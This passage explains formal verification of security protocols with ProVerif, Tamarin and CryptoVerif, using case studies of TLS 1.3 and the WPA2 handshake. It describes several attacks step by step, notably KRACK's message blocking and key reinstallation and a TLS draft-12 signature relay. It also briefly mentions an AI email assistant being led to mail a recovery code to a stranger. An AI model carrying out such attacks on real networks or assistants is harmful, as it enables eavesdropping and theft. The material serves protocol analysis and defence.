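Honest participants become clauses of the same form. If Bob sends M after receiving M<sub>1</sub> and M<sub>2</sub>, the clause is attacker(M<sub>1</sub>) ∧ attacker(M<sub>2</sub>) ⇒ attacker(M), because an attacker who knows M<sub>1</sub> and M<sub>2</sub> can send them to Bob and intercept M. A term s is secret if attacker(s) does not follow from the clauses.

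ProVerif combines clauses by a method called resolution, because the attacker can keep encrypting forever and a list of everything that follows would never end. When one clause's conclusion matches a condition of another, ProVerif merges them into a single clause that skips the intermediate fact. Unrestricted merging would also go on forever, since a condition attacker(x) with an unknown x matches the conclusion of every clause.

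ProVerif therefore selects one part of each clause and merges clauses only at that part. It selects a condition more specific than attacker(x) if there is one, and otherwise the conclusion. *The Security Protocol Verifier ProVerif and its Horn Clause Resolution Algorithm* (Blanchet, 2022) describes this selection as the key to avoiding many endless searches. The decryption clause above has a specific condition, so ProVerif looks for ways to obtain an encrypted term. The encryption clause has none, so ProVerif uses it only where another clause needs an encrypted term.

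When merging produces nothing new, ProVerif keeps only the clauses whose conclusion it selected. A theorem guarantees that these clauses derive the same facts as the original set. ProVerif then only has to check whether any of them concludes attacker(s).

### A small protocol worked through

Blanchet often illustrates the method with a simplified version of Denning and Sacco's protocol, without the timestamp. Let a be Alice's private signing key, b Bob's private key, and pub(z) the public key for a private key z.

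1. Alice creates a fresh key k and sends Bob enc(sign(k, a), pub(b)).
2. Bob checks the signature and sends Alice a secret, as senc(s, k).

Alice will start a run with anyone, so her clause covers every public key x:

attacker(x) ⇒ attacker(enc(sign(k[x], a), x))

Here k[x] stands for the key that Alice creates for the owner of x. ProVerif also attaches a session number to it, which we can leave out. Bob's clause is:

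attacker(enc(sign(y, a), pub(b))) ⇒ attacker(senc(s, y))

ProVerif then combines these with the clauses for the attacker, who can encrypt, decrypt, compute a public key from a private one and read the contents of a signature. The steps that matter are these:

1. attacker(z) ⇒ attacker(sign(k[pub(z)], a)). Anyone with a private key z can get Alice to send him a signed key, and can decrypt her message.
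2. attacker(z) ⇒ attacker(k[pub(z)]). He can also read the key inside the signature.
3. attacker(sign(y, a)) ⇒ attacker(senc(s, y)). Anything Alice has signed can be encrypted again for Bob, who answers with the secret.
4. attacker(z) ⇒ attacker(senc(s, k[pub(z)])). This combines steps 1 and 3.
5. attacker(z) ⇒ attacker(s). The attacker decrypts the message in step 4 with the key from step 2.

The attacker can make up a private key of his own, so attacker(s) follows. This is the flaw that Abadi noticed in 1994.

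One repair is to put the recipient's public key inside the signature. Alice then signs the pair (x, k[x]), and Bob accepts the signature only if it contains pub(b). The attacker can still get keys that Alice creates for him, but Bob will no longer accept them. The attacker can also forward Alice's genuine message to Bob and obtain senc(s, k[pub(b)]). To decrypt it he needs k[pub(b)], which by step 2 he has only if he has b. ProVerif therefore derives attacker(b) ⇒ attacker(s) in place of step 5.

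No clause concludes attacker(b), so ProVerif can do nothing more with this clause. Its selected part is a condition, so ProVerif drops it at the end, and no remaining clause concludes attacker(s). The attacker can't forge Alice's signature either, because no clause concludes attacker(a). So the secret is safe however many sessions anyone runs. Blanchet reports that ProVerif proves secrecy for the repaired protocol.

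### Attacks that cannot happen

A derivation may use a clause any number of times, even if the clause describes a participant who acts only once. As Baelde explains, ProVerif therefore does not distinguish a participant who runs once from one who runs forever. It does not have to count sessions, but its clauses over-approximate the protocol, so some of the attacks they allow are impossible in reality.

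In an example from Blanchet, Alice sends senc(k<sub>1</sub>, k), senc(k<sub>2</sub>, k) and senc(s, (k<sub>1</sub>, k<sub>2</sub>)), the last encrypted with a pair of keys. Bob accepts one message, decrypts it with k, publishes the result and stops. The attacker can learn only one of k<sub>1</sub> and k<sub>2</sub> this way, but needs both to read s. Bob's clause, attacker(senc(y, k)) ⇒ attacker(y), leaves out the fact that he stops, so ProVerif applies it twice, obtains both keys and derives attacker(s).

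ProVerif checks a derivation by trying to reconstruct a run of the actual protocol from it. There are four possible outcomes:

- there is no derivation, and the property holds;
- there is a derivation and a matching run, which is a real attack;
- there is a derivation but ProVerif finds no matching run, and it gives no verdict;
- the search never ends.

The first two kinds of answer are always correct. ProVerif often gives the third when something changes during a run. For example, it cannot prove that a protocol is secure if the protocol keeps a value secret for a while and then reveals it, because its clauses let the attacker use the revealed value from the start. *A little more conversation, a little less action, a lot more satisfaction*, by Cheval, Cortier and Turuani, identifies the same weakness for counters, tables and memory cells.

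The flag in the email assistant is such a memory cell. A direct translation into clauses would keep the fact that the flag is off even after a lookup had turned it on. ProVerif would then derive an attack in which the model looks up the recovery code and mails it to the stranger, even though the scaffold prevents this attack. Cheval and colleagues address such cases with a front end, GSVerif, which transforms the security property before ProVerif tries to prove it.

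Over-approximation needs more care in proofs of authentication. A typical claim is that if Bob finishes a run with Alice, then Alice began one with Bob. Letting Bob finish too often in the model is harmless, because it only makes the claim harder to prove. But if the model lets Alice begin when she really would not, the claim could be true in the model and false in reality. According to Baelde, ProVerif prevents this by recording "Alice began" as a condition in the relevant clauses and never merging on it. If every final clause for "Bob finished" still has that condition, Alice must have begun.

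The fourth outcome, an endless search, can arise from an ordinary exchange. In Needham and Schroeder's shared-key protocol, Bob sends a nonce encrypted with a shared key, and Alice returns the nonce minus 1, encrypted with the same key. The clause that models her step also accepts her own reply as input, so ProVerif derives the nonce minus 2, minus 3 and so on. Adding a different label to each kind of message prevents this, because Alice's reply no longer looks like Bob's message. Blanchet and Andreas Podelski proved in 2003 that resolution always ends for protocols with suitable labels.

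In practice, the failures are rarer than the theory might suggest. In *The security protocol verifier ProVerif and its major recent improvements*, Blanchet (2022) reports that ProVerif takes less than a tenth of a second on small examples and a few minutes on complex ones. It produced no false attacks on secrecy or authentication in his tests on examples from the literature. But those examples are not a random sample, and protocols with counters or memory cells can be much harder to verify.

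### What changed in 2022

*ProVerif with Lemmas, Induction, Fast Subsumption, and Much More* (Blanchet, Cheval and Cortier, 2022) describes a major overhaul of the tool. Users can now state lemmas, which ProVerif proves and then uses in later proofs. They can also state axioms, which ProVerif assumes without proof, so a false axiom can invalidate the final result.

An axiom also solves the problem of Bob's single decryption. The user marks Bob's input as "precise", and ProVerif gives each execution of it a fresh label. The built-in axiom is that two messages received under the same label are equal. The false attack requires one execution to receive both senc(k<sub>1</sub>, k) and senc(k<sub>2</sub>, k), which are different terms, so ProVerif discards the clause and proves that s is secret. Marking an input as precise can slow the search or stop it from ending, so users have to decide where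 it is worthwhile.

Another addition is proof by induction. In one of Blanchet's examples, a memory cell starts at 0 and a participant repeatedly replaces its content i with i + 1. Without induction, ProVerif fails to prove that the cell always holds a natural number. It does not merge the clause for this step with itself, since that would go on forever, and nothing else in the clause guarantees that i is a natural number. With induction, ProVerif may assume the claim for everything that happened earlier in the trace, so i is a natural number, and so is i + 1. The proof of the email assistant's invariant worked in the same way.

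The overhaul also made ProVerif faster. Whenever ProVerif creates a clause, it checks whether a more general existing clause covers the new one, and whether the new one covers any existing clauses. These checks used to take more than 80% of the running time. ProVerif now indexes clauses by simple numerical features, which rule out most pairs without a full comparison. A second index finds the clauses that ProVerif can merge. Blanchet, Cheval and Cortier report "impressive speed-ups on large examples".

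Lemmas have since made new kinds of protocol practical to verify. Certificate transparency, for example, requires a public log of the certificates that websites use to prove their identity. The log is a Merkle tree, a structure that allows short proofs that an entry is present and that nobody has removed older ones. In *Automatic verification of transparency protocols*, Cheval, Moreira and Ryan (2023) note that adding clauses for such a structure often makes ProVerif run forever. They extended the tool's lemmas and axioms so that a user can verify the protocol by assuming a few properties of the log, and then prove separately that a Merkle tree has them.

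### Tamarin keeps track of what has been used up

Schmidt, Meier and colleagues (2012) introduced Tamarin in *Automated Analysis of Diffie-Hellman Protocols and Advanced Security Properties*. Tamarin represents the state of the whole system as a multiset of facts, a collection in which the same fact may appear several times. A rule removes some facts and adds others. Logicians call this multiset rewriting, and Cervesato and colleagues used the same kind of notation.

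Linear facts disappear when a rule uses them, while persistent facts, marked with an exclamation mark, stay. Bob's decryption rule uses up the one linear fact it needs, so he can decrypt only once. The email assistant's flag can also be a linear fact, which a lookup replaces with one recording that the flag is on. Tamarin therefore reports neither of the false attacks described above.

In the repaired protocol, a Tamarin rule for Alice could look like this:

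```
rule Alice_sends_key:
  [ Fr(~k), !SignKey($A, a), !PubKey($B, p) ]
--[ Sent($A, $B, ~k) ]->
  [ Out(enc(sign(<p, ~k>, a), p)) ]
```

- The first line names the rule.
- The second line lists the facts the rule needs. Fr(~k) supplies a fresh value, and Tamarin never supplies the same one twice. The two persistent facts give the signing key of some user A and the public key of some user B. The dollar sign marks a public name, so A and B can be any users.
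- The third line adds an entry to the trace, recording that A has sent k to B. It doesn't affect what anyone can do next, but lemmas can refer to it.
- The last line puts the message on the network. The angle brackets form a pair, so Alice signs the recipient's public key together with k.

The attacker has rules of his own for receiving, building and sending messages. A model can also give him extra powers. A rule that takes the persistent fact holding B's private key and sends that key out on the network lets him compromise any user he likes. If the rule records Reveal(B) in the trace, a lemma can take the compromise into account:

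```
lemma session_key_secret:
  "All A B k #i #j.
     Sent(A, B, k) @ #i & K(k) @ #j
     ==> Ex #r. Reveal(B) @ #r"
```

- The first line names the lemma.
- The second line makes the claim general. It covers all users A and B, all keys k, and all points i and j in the trace.
- The third line states the conditions, that A sent k to B at point i and that the attacker knew k at point j.
- The last line states the conclusion, that at some point r the attacker obtained B's private key.

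The attacker learns a key meant for B only if he compromises B. The lemma also covers dishonest users, who appear in the model as users with revealed keys.

### Searching backwards

To prove a lemma, Tamarin looks for a trace that violates it. Here that would be a trace in which A sends k to B, the attacker knows k, and nobody ever reveals B's private key. Tamarin treats these requirements as constraints on an unknown trace and works backwards from each one. It considers every rule that could have produced the required fact, and adds that rule's own requirements to the constraints.

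1. The attacker knows k. It is a fresh value, so he cannot have guessed it, and he must have extracted it from a message.
2. Alice's rule put k inside a message encrypted for B. Bob uses k only to encrypt the secret, and no one can extract a key from a text encrypted with it.
3. The attacker must therefore have decrypted Alice's message, which requires B's private key.
4. The only rule that sends out B's private key also records Reveal(B), which the constraints exclude.

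Every possibility ends in a contradiction, so no violating trace exists and the lemma holds for any number of sessions. A complete trace without a contradiction would have been an attack. Meadows's tool also searched backwards from an insecure state. In tests by Schmidt and colleagues, Tamarin finished in the vast majority of cases, typically within seconds.

The search can find only attacks that the model's equations allow. Schmidt and colleagues built Tamarin for protocols that use Diffie-Hellman key exchange, in which one participant publishes g<sup>a</sup>, the other publishes g<sup>b</sup>, and both can compute g<sup>ab</sup>. Tamarin treats (g<sup>a</sup>)<sup>b</sup> and (g<sup>b</sup>)<sup>a</sup> as equal, but the 2012 version had no equations for adding exponents. Suppose a participant publishes two random exponents a and b, receives a number x and checks whether g<sup>a</sup> ·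 g<sup>b</sup> = g<sup>x</sup>. A real attacker can pass the check by sending a + b. The attacker in the model could not compute that sum, so a security proof in the model would not rule out this attack.

### Why people have to help

Tamarin's backward search can go on forever. Suppose Bob decrypts any number of messages with k and publishes their contents. When Tamarin searches for how the attacker learned some value, it has to check the case where Bob published it. Bob must then have received the value in encrypted form, and that ciphertext may itself have been part of an earlier message that he decrypted and published, and so on.

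The user can stop this with a helper lemma, such as one stating that everything Bob publishes either came from one of Alice's messages or was already known to the attacker. Tamarin must also prove the helper lemma, usually by induction, but can then use it to cut off the circular explanations. Blanchet compares such lemmas to the invariants that programmers use in proofs about loops. A false helper lemma wastes time but cannot lead to a false proof, because Tamarin will not be able to prove it.

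Cortier, Delaune and colleagues (2022) observe in *Automatic generation of sources lemmas in Tamarin* that users often have to write lemmas even for simple protocols, and they automate one common type. Tamarin also has an interactive mode, in which a user can inspect an unfinished proof and choose which constraint to solve next.

### What each tool gives up

Blanchet compares ProVerif and Tamarin with several other tools. Scyther always finishes. If it can neither find an attack nor prove the protocol for unlimited sessions, it proves the protocol only for a fixed number of sessions. Maude-NPA uses no abstraction, so its answers are exact, but it may run forever.

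| Tool | Sessions covered by a proof | Possible false attacks | Always finishes | Help from the user |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| FDR | fixed number | no | yes | none |
| Scyther | unlimited if possible, otherwise a fixed number | no | yes | none |
| Maude-NPA | unlimited | no | no | none |
| ProVerif | unlimited | yes, leading to no verdict | no | occasional |
| Tamarin | unlimited | no | no | often helper lemmas |

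The tools also differ in the cryptography they can handle. Scyther supports only a fixed set of operations. ProVerif doesn't support associative operations, such as exclusive-or, in which the grouping of the inputs doesn't matter. Tamarin supports some of these, including the multiplication of exponents in Diffie-Hellman.

For a protocol without counters or other changing state, ProVerif is usually the easier choice because it may give a verdict without help. Tamarin is better suited to protocols in which a step can happen only once or a stored value changes, if someone can supply the lemmas. *Unrestricting restrictions in ProVerif* (Cheval, 2023) contrasts ProVerif's "push-button" operation with Tamarin's interactive interface, but the difference has narrowed now that ProVerif accepts lemmas. *Sapic+* (Cheval, Jacomme and colleagues, 2022) presents a platform that lets users pick a suitable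 verifier at any stage of development, so researchers can also postpone the choice.

Using these tools takes expertise, which Wilson, Asplund and Johansson (2026) give in *AutoTam* as one reason why industry rarely uses such methods. They designed a programming language for writing protocols, and their software generates a Tamarin model from each program. They proved that, under the usual assumptions about cryptography, any property that holds on every trace of the model also holds when the program runs. A programmer no longer has to write the model by hand, but someone may still have to help Tamarin finish the proof.

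## TLS 1.3: a full-scale proof with an itemised attacker

Transport Layer Security (TLS) encrypts the traffic between web browsers and websites. For much of its history, its designers responded to published attacks by issuing an extension or changing the next version. Cremers, Horvat and colleagues explain in *A Comprehensive Symbolic Analysis of TLS 1.3* (2017) that practical attacks after 2011 came too fast for that approach. The Internet Engineering Task Force, which standardises internet protocols, began drafting TLS 1.3 in 2014, and its working group invited academic researchers to analyse the drafts before release. Cremers and colleagues modelled draft 21 in Tamarin.

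### The handshake and its variants

A TLS connection begins with a handshake, in which the client and the server agree on session keys. The basic version is not much longer than the protocols in earlier sections:

1. The client sends a nonce and g<sup>x</sup>, where x is a fresh secret exponent.
2. The server answers with its own nonce and g<sup>y</sup>. Both sides can now compute g<sup>xy</sup>, and they use keys derived from it to encrypt the rest of the handshake.
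3. The server sends a certificate, which ties its name to a public key, and signs the transcript, meaning all the messages so far. It adds a checksum of the transcript that only someone with the right keys can compute.
4. The client checks all this and returns a checksum of its own. If the server has asked for a client certificate, the client also sends one and signs the transcript.

The variants make TLS hard to analyse. After a handshake, the server can issue a ticket that lets the client use a pre-shared key next time, with or without a new Diffie-Hellman exchange. A returning client can send data with its first message, but an attacker can replay that data. Later in the connection, either side can change its keys, and the server can ask the client for a certificate. Cremers and colleagues put these into one model, so Tamarin's analysis covers every combination of them in any number of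 sessions. In the model, a basic first handshake alone uses up to 21 rules.

The TLS 1.3 specification lists eight properties that the handshake should have. Cremers and colleagues modelled six:

- both sides end up with the same session keys;
- nobody else knows those keys;
- an authenticated party is who the other side believes it to be;
- every run produces different keys;
- an attacker who steals a long-term key cannot read sessions that finished earlier (forward secrecy);
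- an attacker who steals Alice's long-term key cannot use it to pose as Bob to Alice (resistance to key compromise impersonation).

The proof does not cover whether the participants' identities stay hidden, or protection against downgrades, in which an attacker pushes the two sides into using an older version of the protocol or a weaker algorithm.

### A separate action for every kind of theft

The specification assumes a Dolev-Yao attacker. Cremers and colleagues also let the attacker obtain a participant's long-term signing key, a pre-shared key or a Diffie-Hellman exponent. The trace records each of these actions, as in the earlier Tamarin example.

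TLS cannot withstand all of these together. Anyone who has recorded a handshake and obtains x can compute g<sup>xy</sup>, and with it the session keys. Each lemma therefore lists the thefts that must not have happened. With shorter variable names, the lemma for the secrecy of session keys looks like this:

```
lemma secret_session_keys:
  "All s A B w r status #i.
     SessionKey(s, A, B, <status, 'auth'>, <w, r>) @ #i
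   & not (Ex #t. RevLtk(B) @ #t & #t < #i)
   & not (Ex s2 x #t. RevDHExp(s2, B, x) @ #t & #t < #i)
   & not (Ex s3 y #t. RevDHExp(s3, A, y) @ #t & #t < #i)
   & not (Ex p #t. RevealPSK(A, p) @ #t)
   & not (Ex q #t. RevealPSK(B, q) @ #t)
   ==> not Ex #j. K(r) @ #j"
```

- *SessionKey*: at time i, participant A has finished a handshake in session s. A believes that the other side is B, has authenticated B, and holds the key w for writing and r for reading.
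- *RevLtk(B)*: the attacker did not obtain B's signing key before time i. If he had, he could simply have acted as B. He may obtain it afterwards, so the lemma also establishes forward secrecy.
- *RevDHExp*, for B and then for A: the attacker obtained no exponent of either participant before time i.
- *RevealPSK*, for A and then for B: the attacker never obtains a pre-shared key of either participant, even later. This clause has no time limit because a handshake with only a pre-shared key does not provide forward secrecy.
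- *K(r)*: under these conditions, the attacker never learns the read key.

The lemma covers only the read key because each side's read key is the other's write key. If both sides have authenticated each other, applying the lemma to each covers both keys.

Wiggers and Hoyland point out in *Building Confidence in Cryptographic Protocols* that although the lemma excludes the use of some attacker powers against the parties to a session, the attacker may still use them on everybody else. If a theft from Charlie exposed a session between Alice and Bob, Tamarin could not prove the lemma. No clause in the list mentions A's own signing key, so the attacker may have it from the start. The authentication lemmas leave it out too. Cremers and colleagues use these omissions to establish resistance to key compromise impersonation.

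Some exclusions are broader than necessary. The clauses about exponents cover every session of A and B, so the lemma gives no guarantee once the attacker has stolen an exponent from any of their earlier sessions, even an unrelated one. The clauses about pre-shared keys are too strict for handshakes that include a Diffie-Hellman exchange. A second lemma covers these handshakes and holds even if the attacker obtains pre-shared keys after the session keys are established.

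The email assistant's proof could list its assumptions in the same way. The model would let the attacker add an address to the approved list, and the property would be that a stranger receives mail after a lookup only if the attacker has done so.

### A client that doesn't know whether the server has accepted it

Tamarin proved the six properties, with one qualification about authentication. When a server asks for a client's certificate, it may reject what it receives and continue without notifying the client. The client cannot tell from later messages whether the server treats it as authenticated. Cremers and colleagues noticed this while modelling certificate requests that come after the handshake. They added a variable to each side to record its view of the connection, and found that the two views can differ. The working group confirmed that the same mismatch can occur in the main handshake.

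The paper gives an example of the harm this could do. A server stores whatever authenticated clients send in a secure database and writes everything else to an insecure log. It asks a client for a certificate, rejects the one it gets and continues the connection. The client assumes it has been accepted and sends sensitive data, which the server writes to the insecure log. This can happen without an attacker and violates none of the eight stated properties, because the specification requires the two sides to agree on who they are but not on whether the server has accepted the client. The working group decided not to change this, so an application that needs confirmation has to provide its own.

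A related problem turned up in draft 18, which Bhargavan, Blanchet and Kobeissi analysed in *Verified Models and Reference Implementations for the TLS 1.3 Standard Candidate* (2017). The server may start sending data before it receives the client's certificate. If an attacker delays the certificate, the client may treat data meant for an anonymous visitor as its own personal data.

### Old versions and weak algorithms

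Cremers and colleagues assumed that cryptography is perfect and that everybody uses TLS 1.3. Real servers also support older versions, some with algorithms that attackers can break. Bhargavan and colleagues added these weaknesses to a ProVerif model as further items. In the model, for example, a server may choose a weak Diffie-Hellman group, in which the attacker knows every result, or a weak hash function, which gives the same output for every input.

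The researchers found the exceptions by repeatedly using ProVerif to check whether a message stays secret. Each time it returned an attack, they added the condition behind that attack to the list of exceptions and ran the check again. For TLS 1.2, they needed five exceptions before the proof succeeded. Two of these affect more than the session in which the weakness occurs. If a server uses a weak form of RSA decryption or signs with a weak hash function even once, every session that relies on the same server key is at risk.

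This matters for TLS 1.3 because a server may use the same key for TLS 1.2 and TLS 1.3. When Bhargavan and colleagues analysed the two versions together, ProVerif found that an attacker could use the old RSA decryption to forge the server's signature in TLS 1.3. It also found a forgery that uses weak hash functions. TLS 1.3 had already removed the weak RSA mode, but that does not prevent the first attack if the server still offers the mode to older clients. With the weak algorithms disabled in TLS 1.2, ProVerif proved the expected properties of the main TLS 1.3 handshake.

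They also found an attack on earlier drafts that closely resembles Lowe's. Up to draft 12, a returning client could sign the data it sent with its first message. Suppose Alice shares one pre-shared key with a dishonest server Z, and Z shares another with an honest server Bob.

1. Alice sends Z her certificate, her signature and a request, encrypted with a key derived from the one she shares with Z.
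2. Z decrypts all of this and encrypts it again with a key derived from the one he shares with Bob.
3. Bob finds a valid signature from Alice and carries out the request as if she had sent it to him.

On the web, Z may be able to choose the request, because a page from his site can make Alice's browser send it. As in Denning and Sacco's protocol, nothing in the signed text tied it to the intended recipient. Draft 13 added a value derived from the pre-shared key to what the client signs, and the working group later removed this use of client certificates.

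### One large model or several smaller proofs

Bhargavan and colleagues also wanted a proof that does not assume perfect encryption. They used CryptoVerif, a tool in which messages are strings of bits and the attacker is any program that runs in polynomial time and may make random guesses. Its proofs show that such an attacker has only a negligible chance of success, provided that the underlying algorithms meet standard assumptions and a few less usual ones. CryptoVerif needs guidance from an expert, and the whole protocol was too much for it. They therefore proved three parts separately and joined the results by hand:

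1. The first handshake produces keys that the attacker cannot distinguish from fresh random values, so the argument can replace them with random values.
2. The part of TLS that encrypts application data is secure if its keys are random, and step 1 provides such keys.
3. A handshake with a random pre-shared key produces new keys that also look random, including the next pre-shared key. The argument can therefore be repeated for any number of later connections.

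Cremers and colleagues model issuing a ticket and using it later as events in the same trace, so the two don't have to be joined by hand. Their model also covers certificate requests after the handshake, which Bhargavan and colleagues left out. But one large model takes far more computation, and changing any part of it may affect every proof.

Joining proofs by hand can also leave some combinations of features uncovered. The CryptoVerif proofs do not cover a handshake that uses both a pre-shared key and a client certificate. The attack on draft 12 exploited that combination, and an earlier Tamarin analysis had found a flaw in draft 10 that also involved it. The ProVerif model does include it. CryptoVerif also failed to prove forward secrecy for handshakes that combine a pre-shared key with Diffie-Hellman. Bhargavan and colleagues attribute this to a limitation of the tool, and Tamarin did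 prove the property in the symbolic model.

### What the proofs cost

Cremers and colleagues estimate that the modelling took about three months. They spent most of that time on lemmas that break the proof into pieces Tamarin can handle by itself. Their map of the proof shows nine main lemmas and about forty helper lemmas. After that, proving everything took about a week, and a person had to guide Tamarin through the harder lemmas. Tamarin needed over 10 GB of memory to load the model and could use 100 GB during a proof. One proof it found automatically was almost a million lines long. Rechecking the finished proofs takes about a day.

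In *A tale of two models* (2022), Celi, Hoyland and colleagues later prove the security of KEMTLS without manual proof steps. KEMTLS is a proposed variant of TLS designed for quantum-resistant cryptography. The client uses the public key in the server's certificate to send a secret that only the server can recover, and the server proves its identity by using that secret instead of signing. Celi and colleagues adapted the TLS 1.3 model and added helper lemmas until Tamarin could prove every lemma unaided. The proof takes 42 hours on a machine with 80 cores and 192 GiB of memory, and Wiggers and Hoyland give its length as nearly 500,000 lines.

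The comparison with the original is not quite fair, because Celi and colleagues switched off pre-shared keys and tickets. They also think that removing Diffie-Hellman may have made the proof easier for Tamarin. The automatic proof still took manual work to set up, including many hours spent finding out which helper lemmas hindered Tamarin's proof search and had to be hidden.

Automation helped Celi and colleagues find a mistake in the model they had inherited. One of its main lemmas should state that the client and server agree on their keys, but the published version compared the client's pair of read key and write key with the server's. These pairs are never equal in a correct run, because the client reads with the key the server writes with. The stored proof used the right comparison, so somebody had apparently changed the lemma after proving it. They remark that such a slip is easy to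 imagine when even a small change means days of manual proving.

| Analysis | Work by people | Work by machines |
|---|---|---|
| Cremers and colleagues, Tamarin | about 3 months | about a week with manual guidance, up to 100 GB of memory |
| Bhargavan and colleagues, ProVerif | 3 person-weeks | 70 minutes |
| Bhargavan and colleagues, CryptoVerif | 5 person-weeks | 6 minutes |
| Celi and colleagues, Tamarin | no figure given | 42 hours on 80 cores, 192 GiB of memory |

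The difference between three months and three weeks does not show that one tool is better, because the two 2017 teams covered different things and a ProVerif expert did the three weeks of work.

Symbolic Software's *Verifpal Takes on TLS 1.3* describes a run completed in September 2026. Verifpal, a protocol verifier with a simplified modelling language meant to make it easier to use, checked 19 queries with two concurrent sessions per participant. The run needed more memory than a 64 GB computer had, and finished on a rented one with 256 GB. Verifpal found no attack for 16 of the queries, and for the other three it found attacks that the developers had predicted. For instance, the attacker can pose as a client and learn the server's first handshake key before the server has authenticated anybody. Verifpal no longer finds this attack if the query covers only runs in which the server goes on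 to send application data.

This is weaker evidence than a proof in Tamarin or ProVerif, since Symbolic Software warns that Verifpal can miss attacks even with only two sessions. The model also covers less, omitting handshakes with pre-shared keys and algorithm negotiation. The signing keys leak only after all the handshakes have finished, so the run could not test resistance to key compromise impersonation.

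### Language models that write the protocol model

Most of the human work in these projects went into writing rules and lemmas, and language models can now do some of it. *MASTA* (Xiao, Deng and colleagues, 2026) presents a system that turns an ordinary English description of a protocol into a Tamarin model without human help. One agent writes the rules and another writes the lemmas. A third reads Tamarin's verdicts and decides which of the other two has to fix what. After each new rule, Tamarin checks that an honest run can still take place, because otherwise a model that does nothing would pass.

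Xiao and colleagues tested MASTA on 10 protocols and 139 altered versions of them. Of the altered versions, 101 have a different message exchange but remain secure, and 38 contain a flaw the researchers introduced. They compared MASTA, running on Qwen 3.5-plus, with three general coding agents: Codex with GPT-5.5, Claude Code with Opus 4.7, and OpenCode, also with Qwen 3.5-plus. All scores run from 0 to 1.

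| What the score measures | MASTA | Best of the other three |
|---|---|---|
| Steps of the protocol match the reference model | 0.829 | 0.762 |
| Lemmas match the reference lemmas | 0.699 | 0.643 |
| Tamarin's verdicts match those on the reference model | 0.567 | 0.594 |
| Harmless changes appear in the model | 0.745 | 0.758 |
| Tamarin detects the introduced flaw | 1.000 | 0.961 |

MASTA averaged 21 minutes and about 10 calls to Tamarin per task. That is far less than three months, but the benchmark includes only protocols that Tamarin can prove unaided within ten minutes, which rules out anything like the full TLS model. Some of the protocols are well known, and the language models may have seen published Tamarin models of them during training.

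The perfect score in the last row is less impressive than it looks. A flaw counts as detected if Tamarin refutes at least one of the lemmas that the flaw should make false, but a faulty model could fail the same lemma for an unrelated reason, and the score doesn't penalise false alarms. Xiao and colleagues argue that the other scores already reflect such errors. The third row is therefore more useful to somebody who wants to know whether a protocol is secure, and MASTA gets little more than half the available credit in that row. That score also gives only partial credit for a proof much shorter than the reference proof, since a very short proof may mean that the protocol in the model hardly runs.

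In the benchmark, a human expert had checked the altered descriptions and their reference models, but a user with a new protocol has no reference model. Tamarin can prove that the lemmas follow from the rules, but not that the rules describe the protocol. Someone who understands both the rules and the protocol still has to compare them.

In 2017, Cremers and colleagues published the specification with notes showing which rule in their Tamarin model represents each part and what the model omits, so readers can check the model against the specification without learning Tamarin's notation. Bhargavan and colleagues instead wrote an implementation, RefTLS, and generated a ProVerif model from its 1,000-line core. In that model, the attacker may call the core's functions in any order, so the proof does not depend on the application around the core. The proof still relies on the unverified translation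 from code to model and on about 3,000 lines of trusted libraries, mostly for reading and writing messages.

A careful comparison can still miss an assumption that nobody questioned. According to Wiggers and Hoyland, the TLS 1.3 proof initially assumed that nobody uses the same certificate as both a client and a server, although the specification does not forbid it. This gap led to the "Selfie" attack, in which a client can be tricked into connecting to itself.

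## WPA2: a proved protocol that was broken

A gap in a proof had already caused a more serious failure in Wi-Fi. Researchers proved the WPA2 handshake secure in 2005. In 2017, two other researchers showed how to decrypt the traffic without violating the properties the proof had established.

WPA2 (Wi-Fi Protected Access 2) encrypts the traffic between a device, such as a laptop, and an access point, usually a router. It belongs to IEEE 802.11, a standard of more than 3,000 pages. The laptop and the router start with a shared master key, which on a home network comes from the password. A handshake of four messages then gives them a session key:

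1. The router sends a nonce.
2. The laptop chooses its own nonce and computes the session key from the master key and the two nonces. It sends its nonce with a checksum that only someone with the session key can compute.
3. The router computes the same session key and verifies the checksum. It sends the group key, which protects broadcasts to all devices on the network, encrypted with the session key and with a checksum of its own.
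4. The laptop installs both keys and sends a confirmation. When this arrives, the router installs the session key too.

The router also numbers its handshake messages so that the laptop can reject old copies. The laptop computes the session key in step 2 but doesn't encrypt anything with it until it installs the key in step 4.

### The 2005 proof

*A Modular Correctness Proof of IEEE 802.11i and TLS* (He, Sundararajan and colleagues, 2005) analyses this handshake, the shorter one that later distributes new group keys, and TLS, which can supply the master key in place of a password. The paper uses a logic that builds the proof of a large protocol from proofs of its parts. It proves each part separately, with its own invariants, then shows that these invariants still hold when the parts run together.

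The proof showed that the session keys stay secret and that the handshake provides authentication, meaning that a laptop and a router that complete it are really dealing with each other. According to Stanford Security Lab's *Protocol Composition Logic (PCL)*, the logic and a related model-checking method also uncovered serious vulnerabilities in 802.11i, the part of the Wi-Fi standard behind WPA2, and the standards body adopted the suggested fixes.

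Other researchers proved the security of the encryption that WPA2 applies to data after the handshake. Vanhoef (2017), in *Key Reinstallation Attacks*, lists both proofs among the reasons the handshake seemed secure. Another was that, apart from password guessing, nobody had found an attack in over a decade.

### How a repeated message undoes the encryption

WPA2 allows three encryption methods, which all work roughly the same way. The sender keeps a counter that starts at a set value and goes up by one with every message. The standard calls the counter value a nonce, although it isn't random. The sender computes a string of random-looking bits, the keystream, from the key and the counter value, then combines it with the message by exclusive-or, which gives 0 where two bits are equal and 1 where they differ.

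Suppose the message is 0110 and the keystream is 1011. The encrypted message is 1101, which reveals nothing about the message to someone without the keystream. But if the counter returns to an earlier value under the same key, the cipher produces the same keystream again, and a second message, 1100, is encrypted as 0111. An attacker who knows or guesses the first message can combine it with 1101 to recover the keystream, and then read the second message. If he knows neither message, he can still combine 1101 with 0111 to get 1010, which has a 1 wherever the two messages differ.

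Installing the session key sets its counter to 0. This is harmless if it happens once, but Wi-Fi often loses messages, so a router that receives no confirmation sends message 3 again. Mathy Vanhoef and Frank Piessens exploited this in their key reinstallation attack, or KRACK:

1. The attacker places himself between the laptop and the router and forwards the first three messages unchanged.
2. The laptop installs the session key and sends its confirmation, which the attacker blocks.
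3. The laptop starts to send encrypted data, and its counter goes up.
4. The router sends message 3 again with a new number, so the laptop does not reject it as an old copy. The attacker lets it through.
5. The laptop installs the same key a second time and sets the counter back to 0. Its next messages reuse the earlier keystream.

The attacker only blocks one message and forwards the others, and both devices follow the standard throughout. Some laptops accept only encrypted messages after installing a key, which stops this simple version of the attack. Vanhoef and Piessens later got around this by abusing a flag from Wi-Fi's power-saving features.

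Reusing a counter value lets the attacker decrypt and replay messages under any of the three encryption methods. He can also forge messages in one direction under TKIP and in both directions under GCMP.

### What the proof had left out

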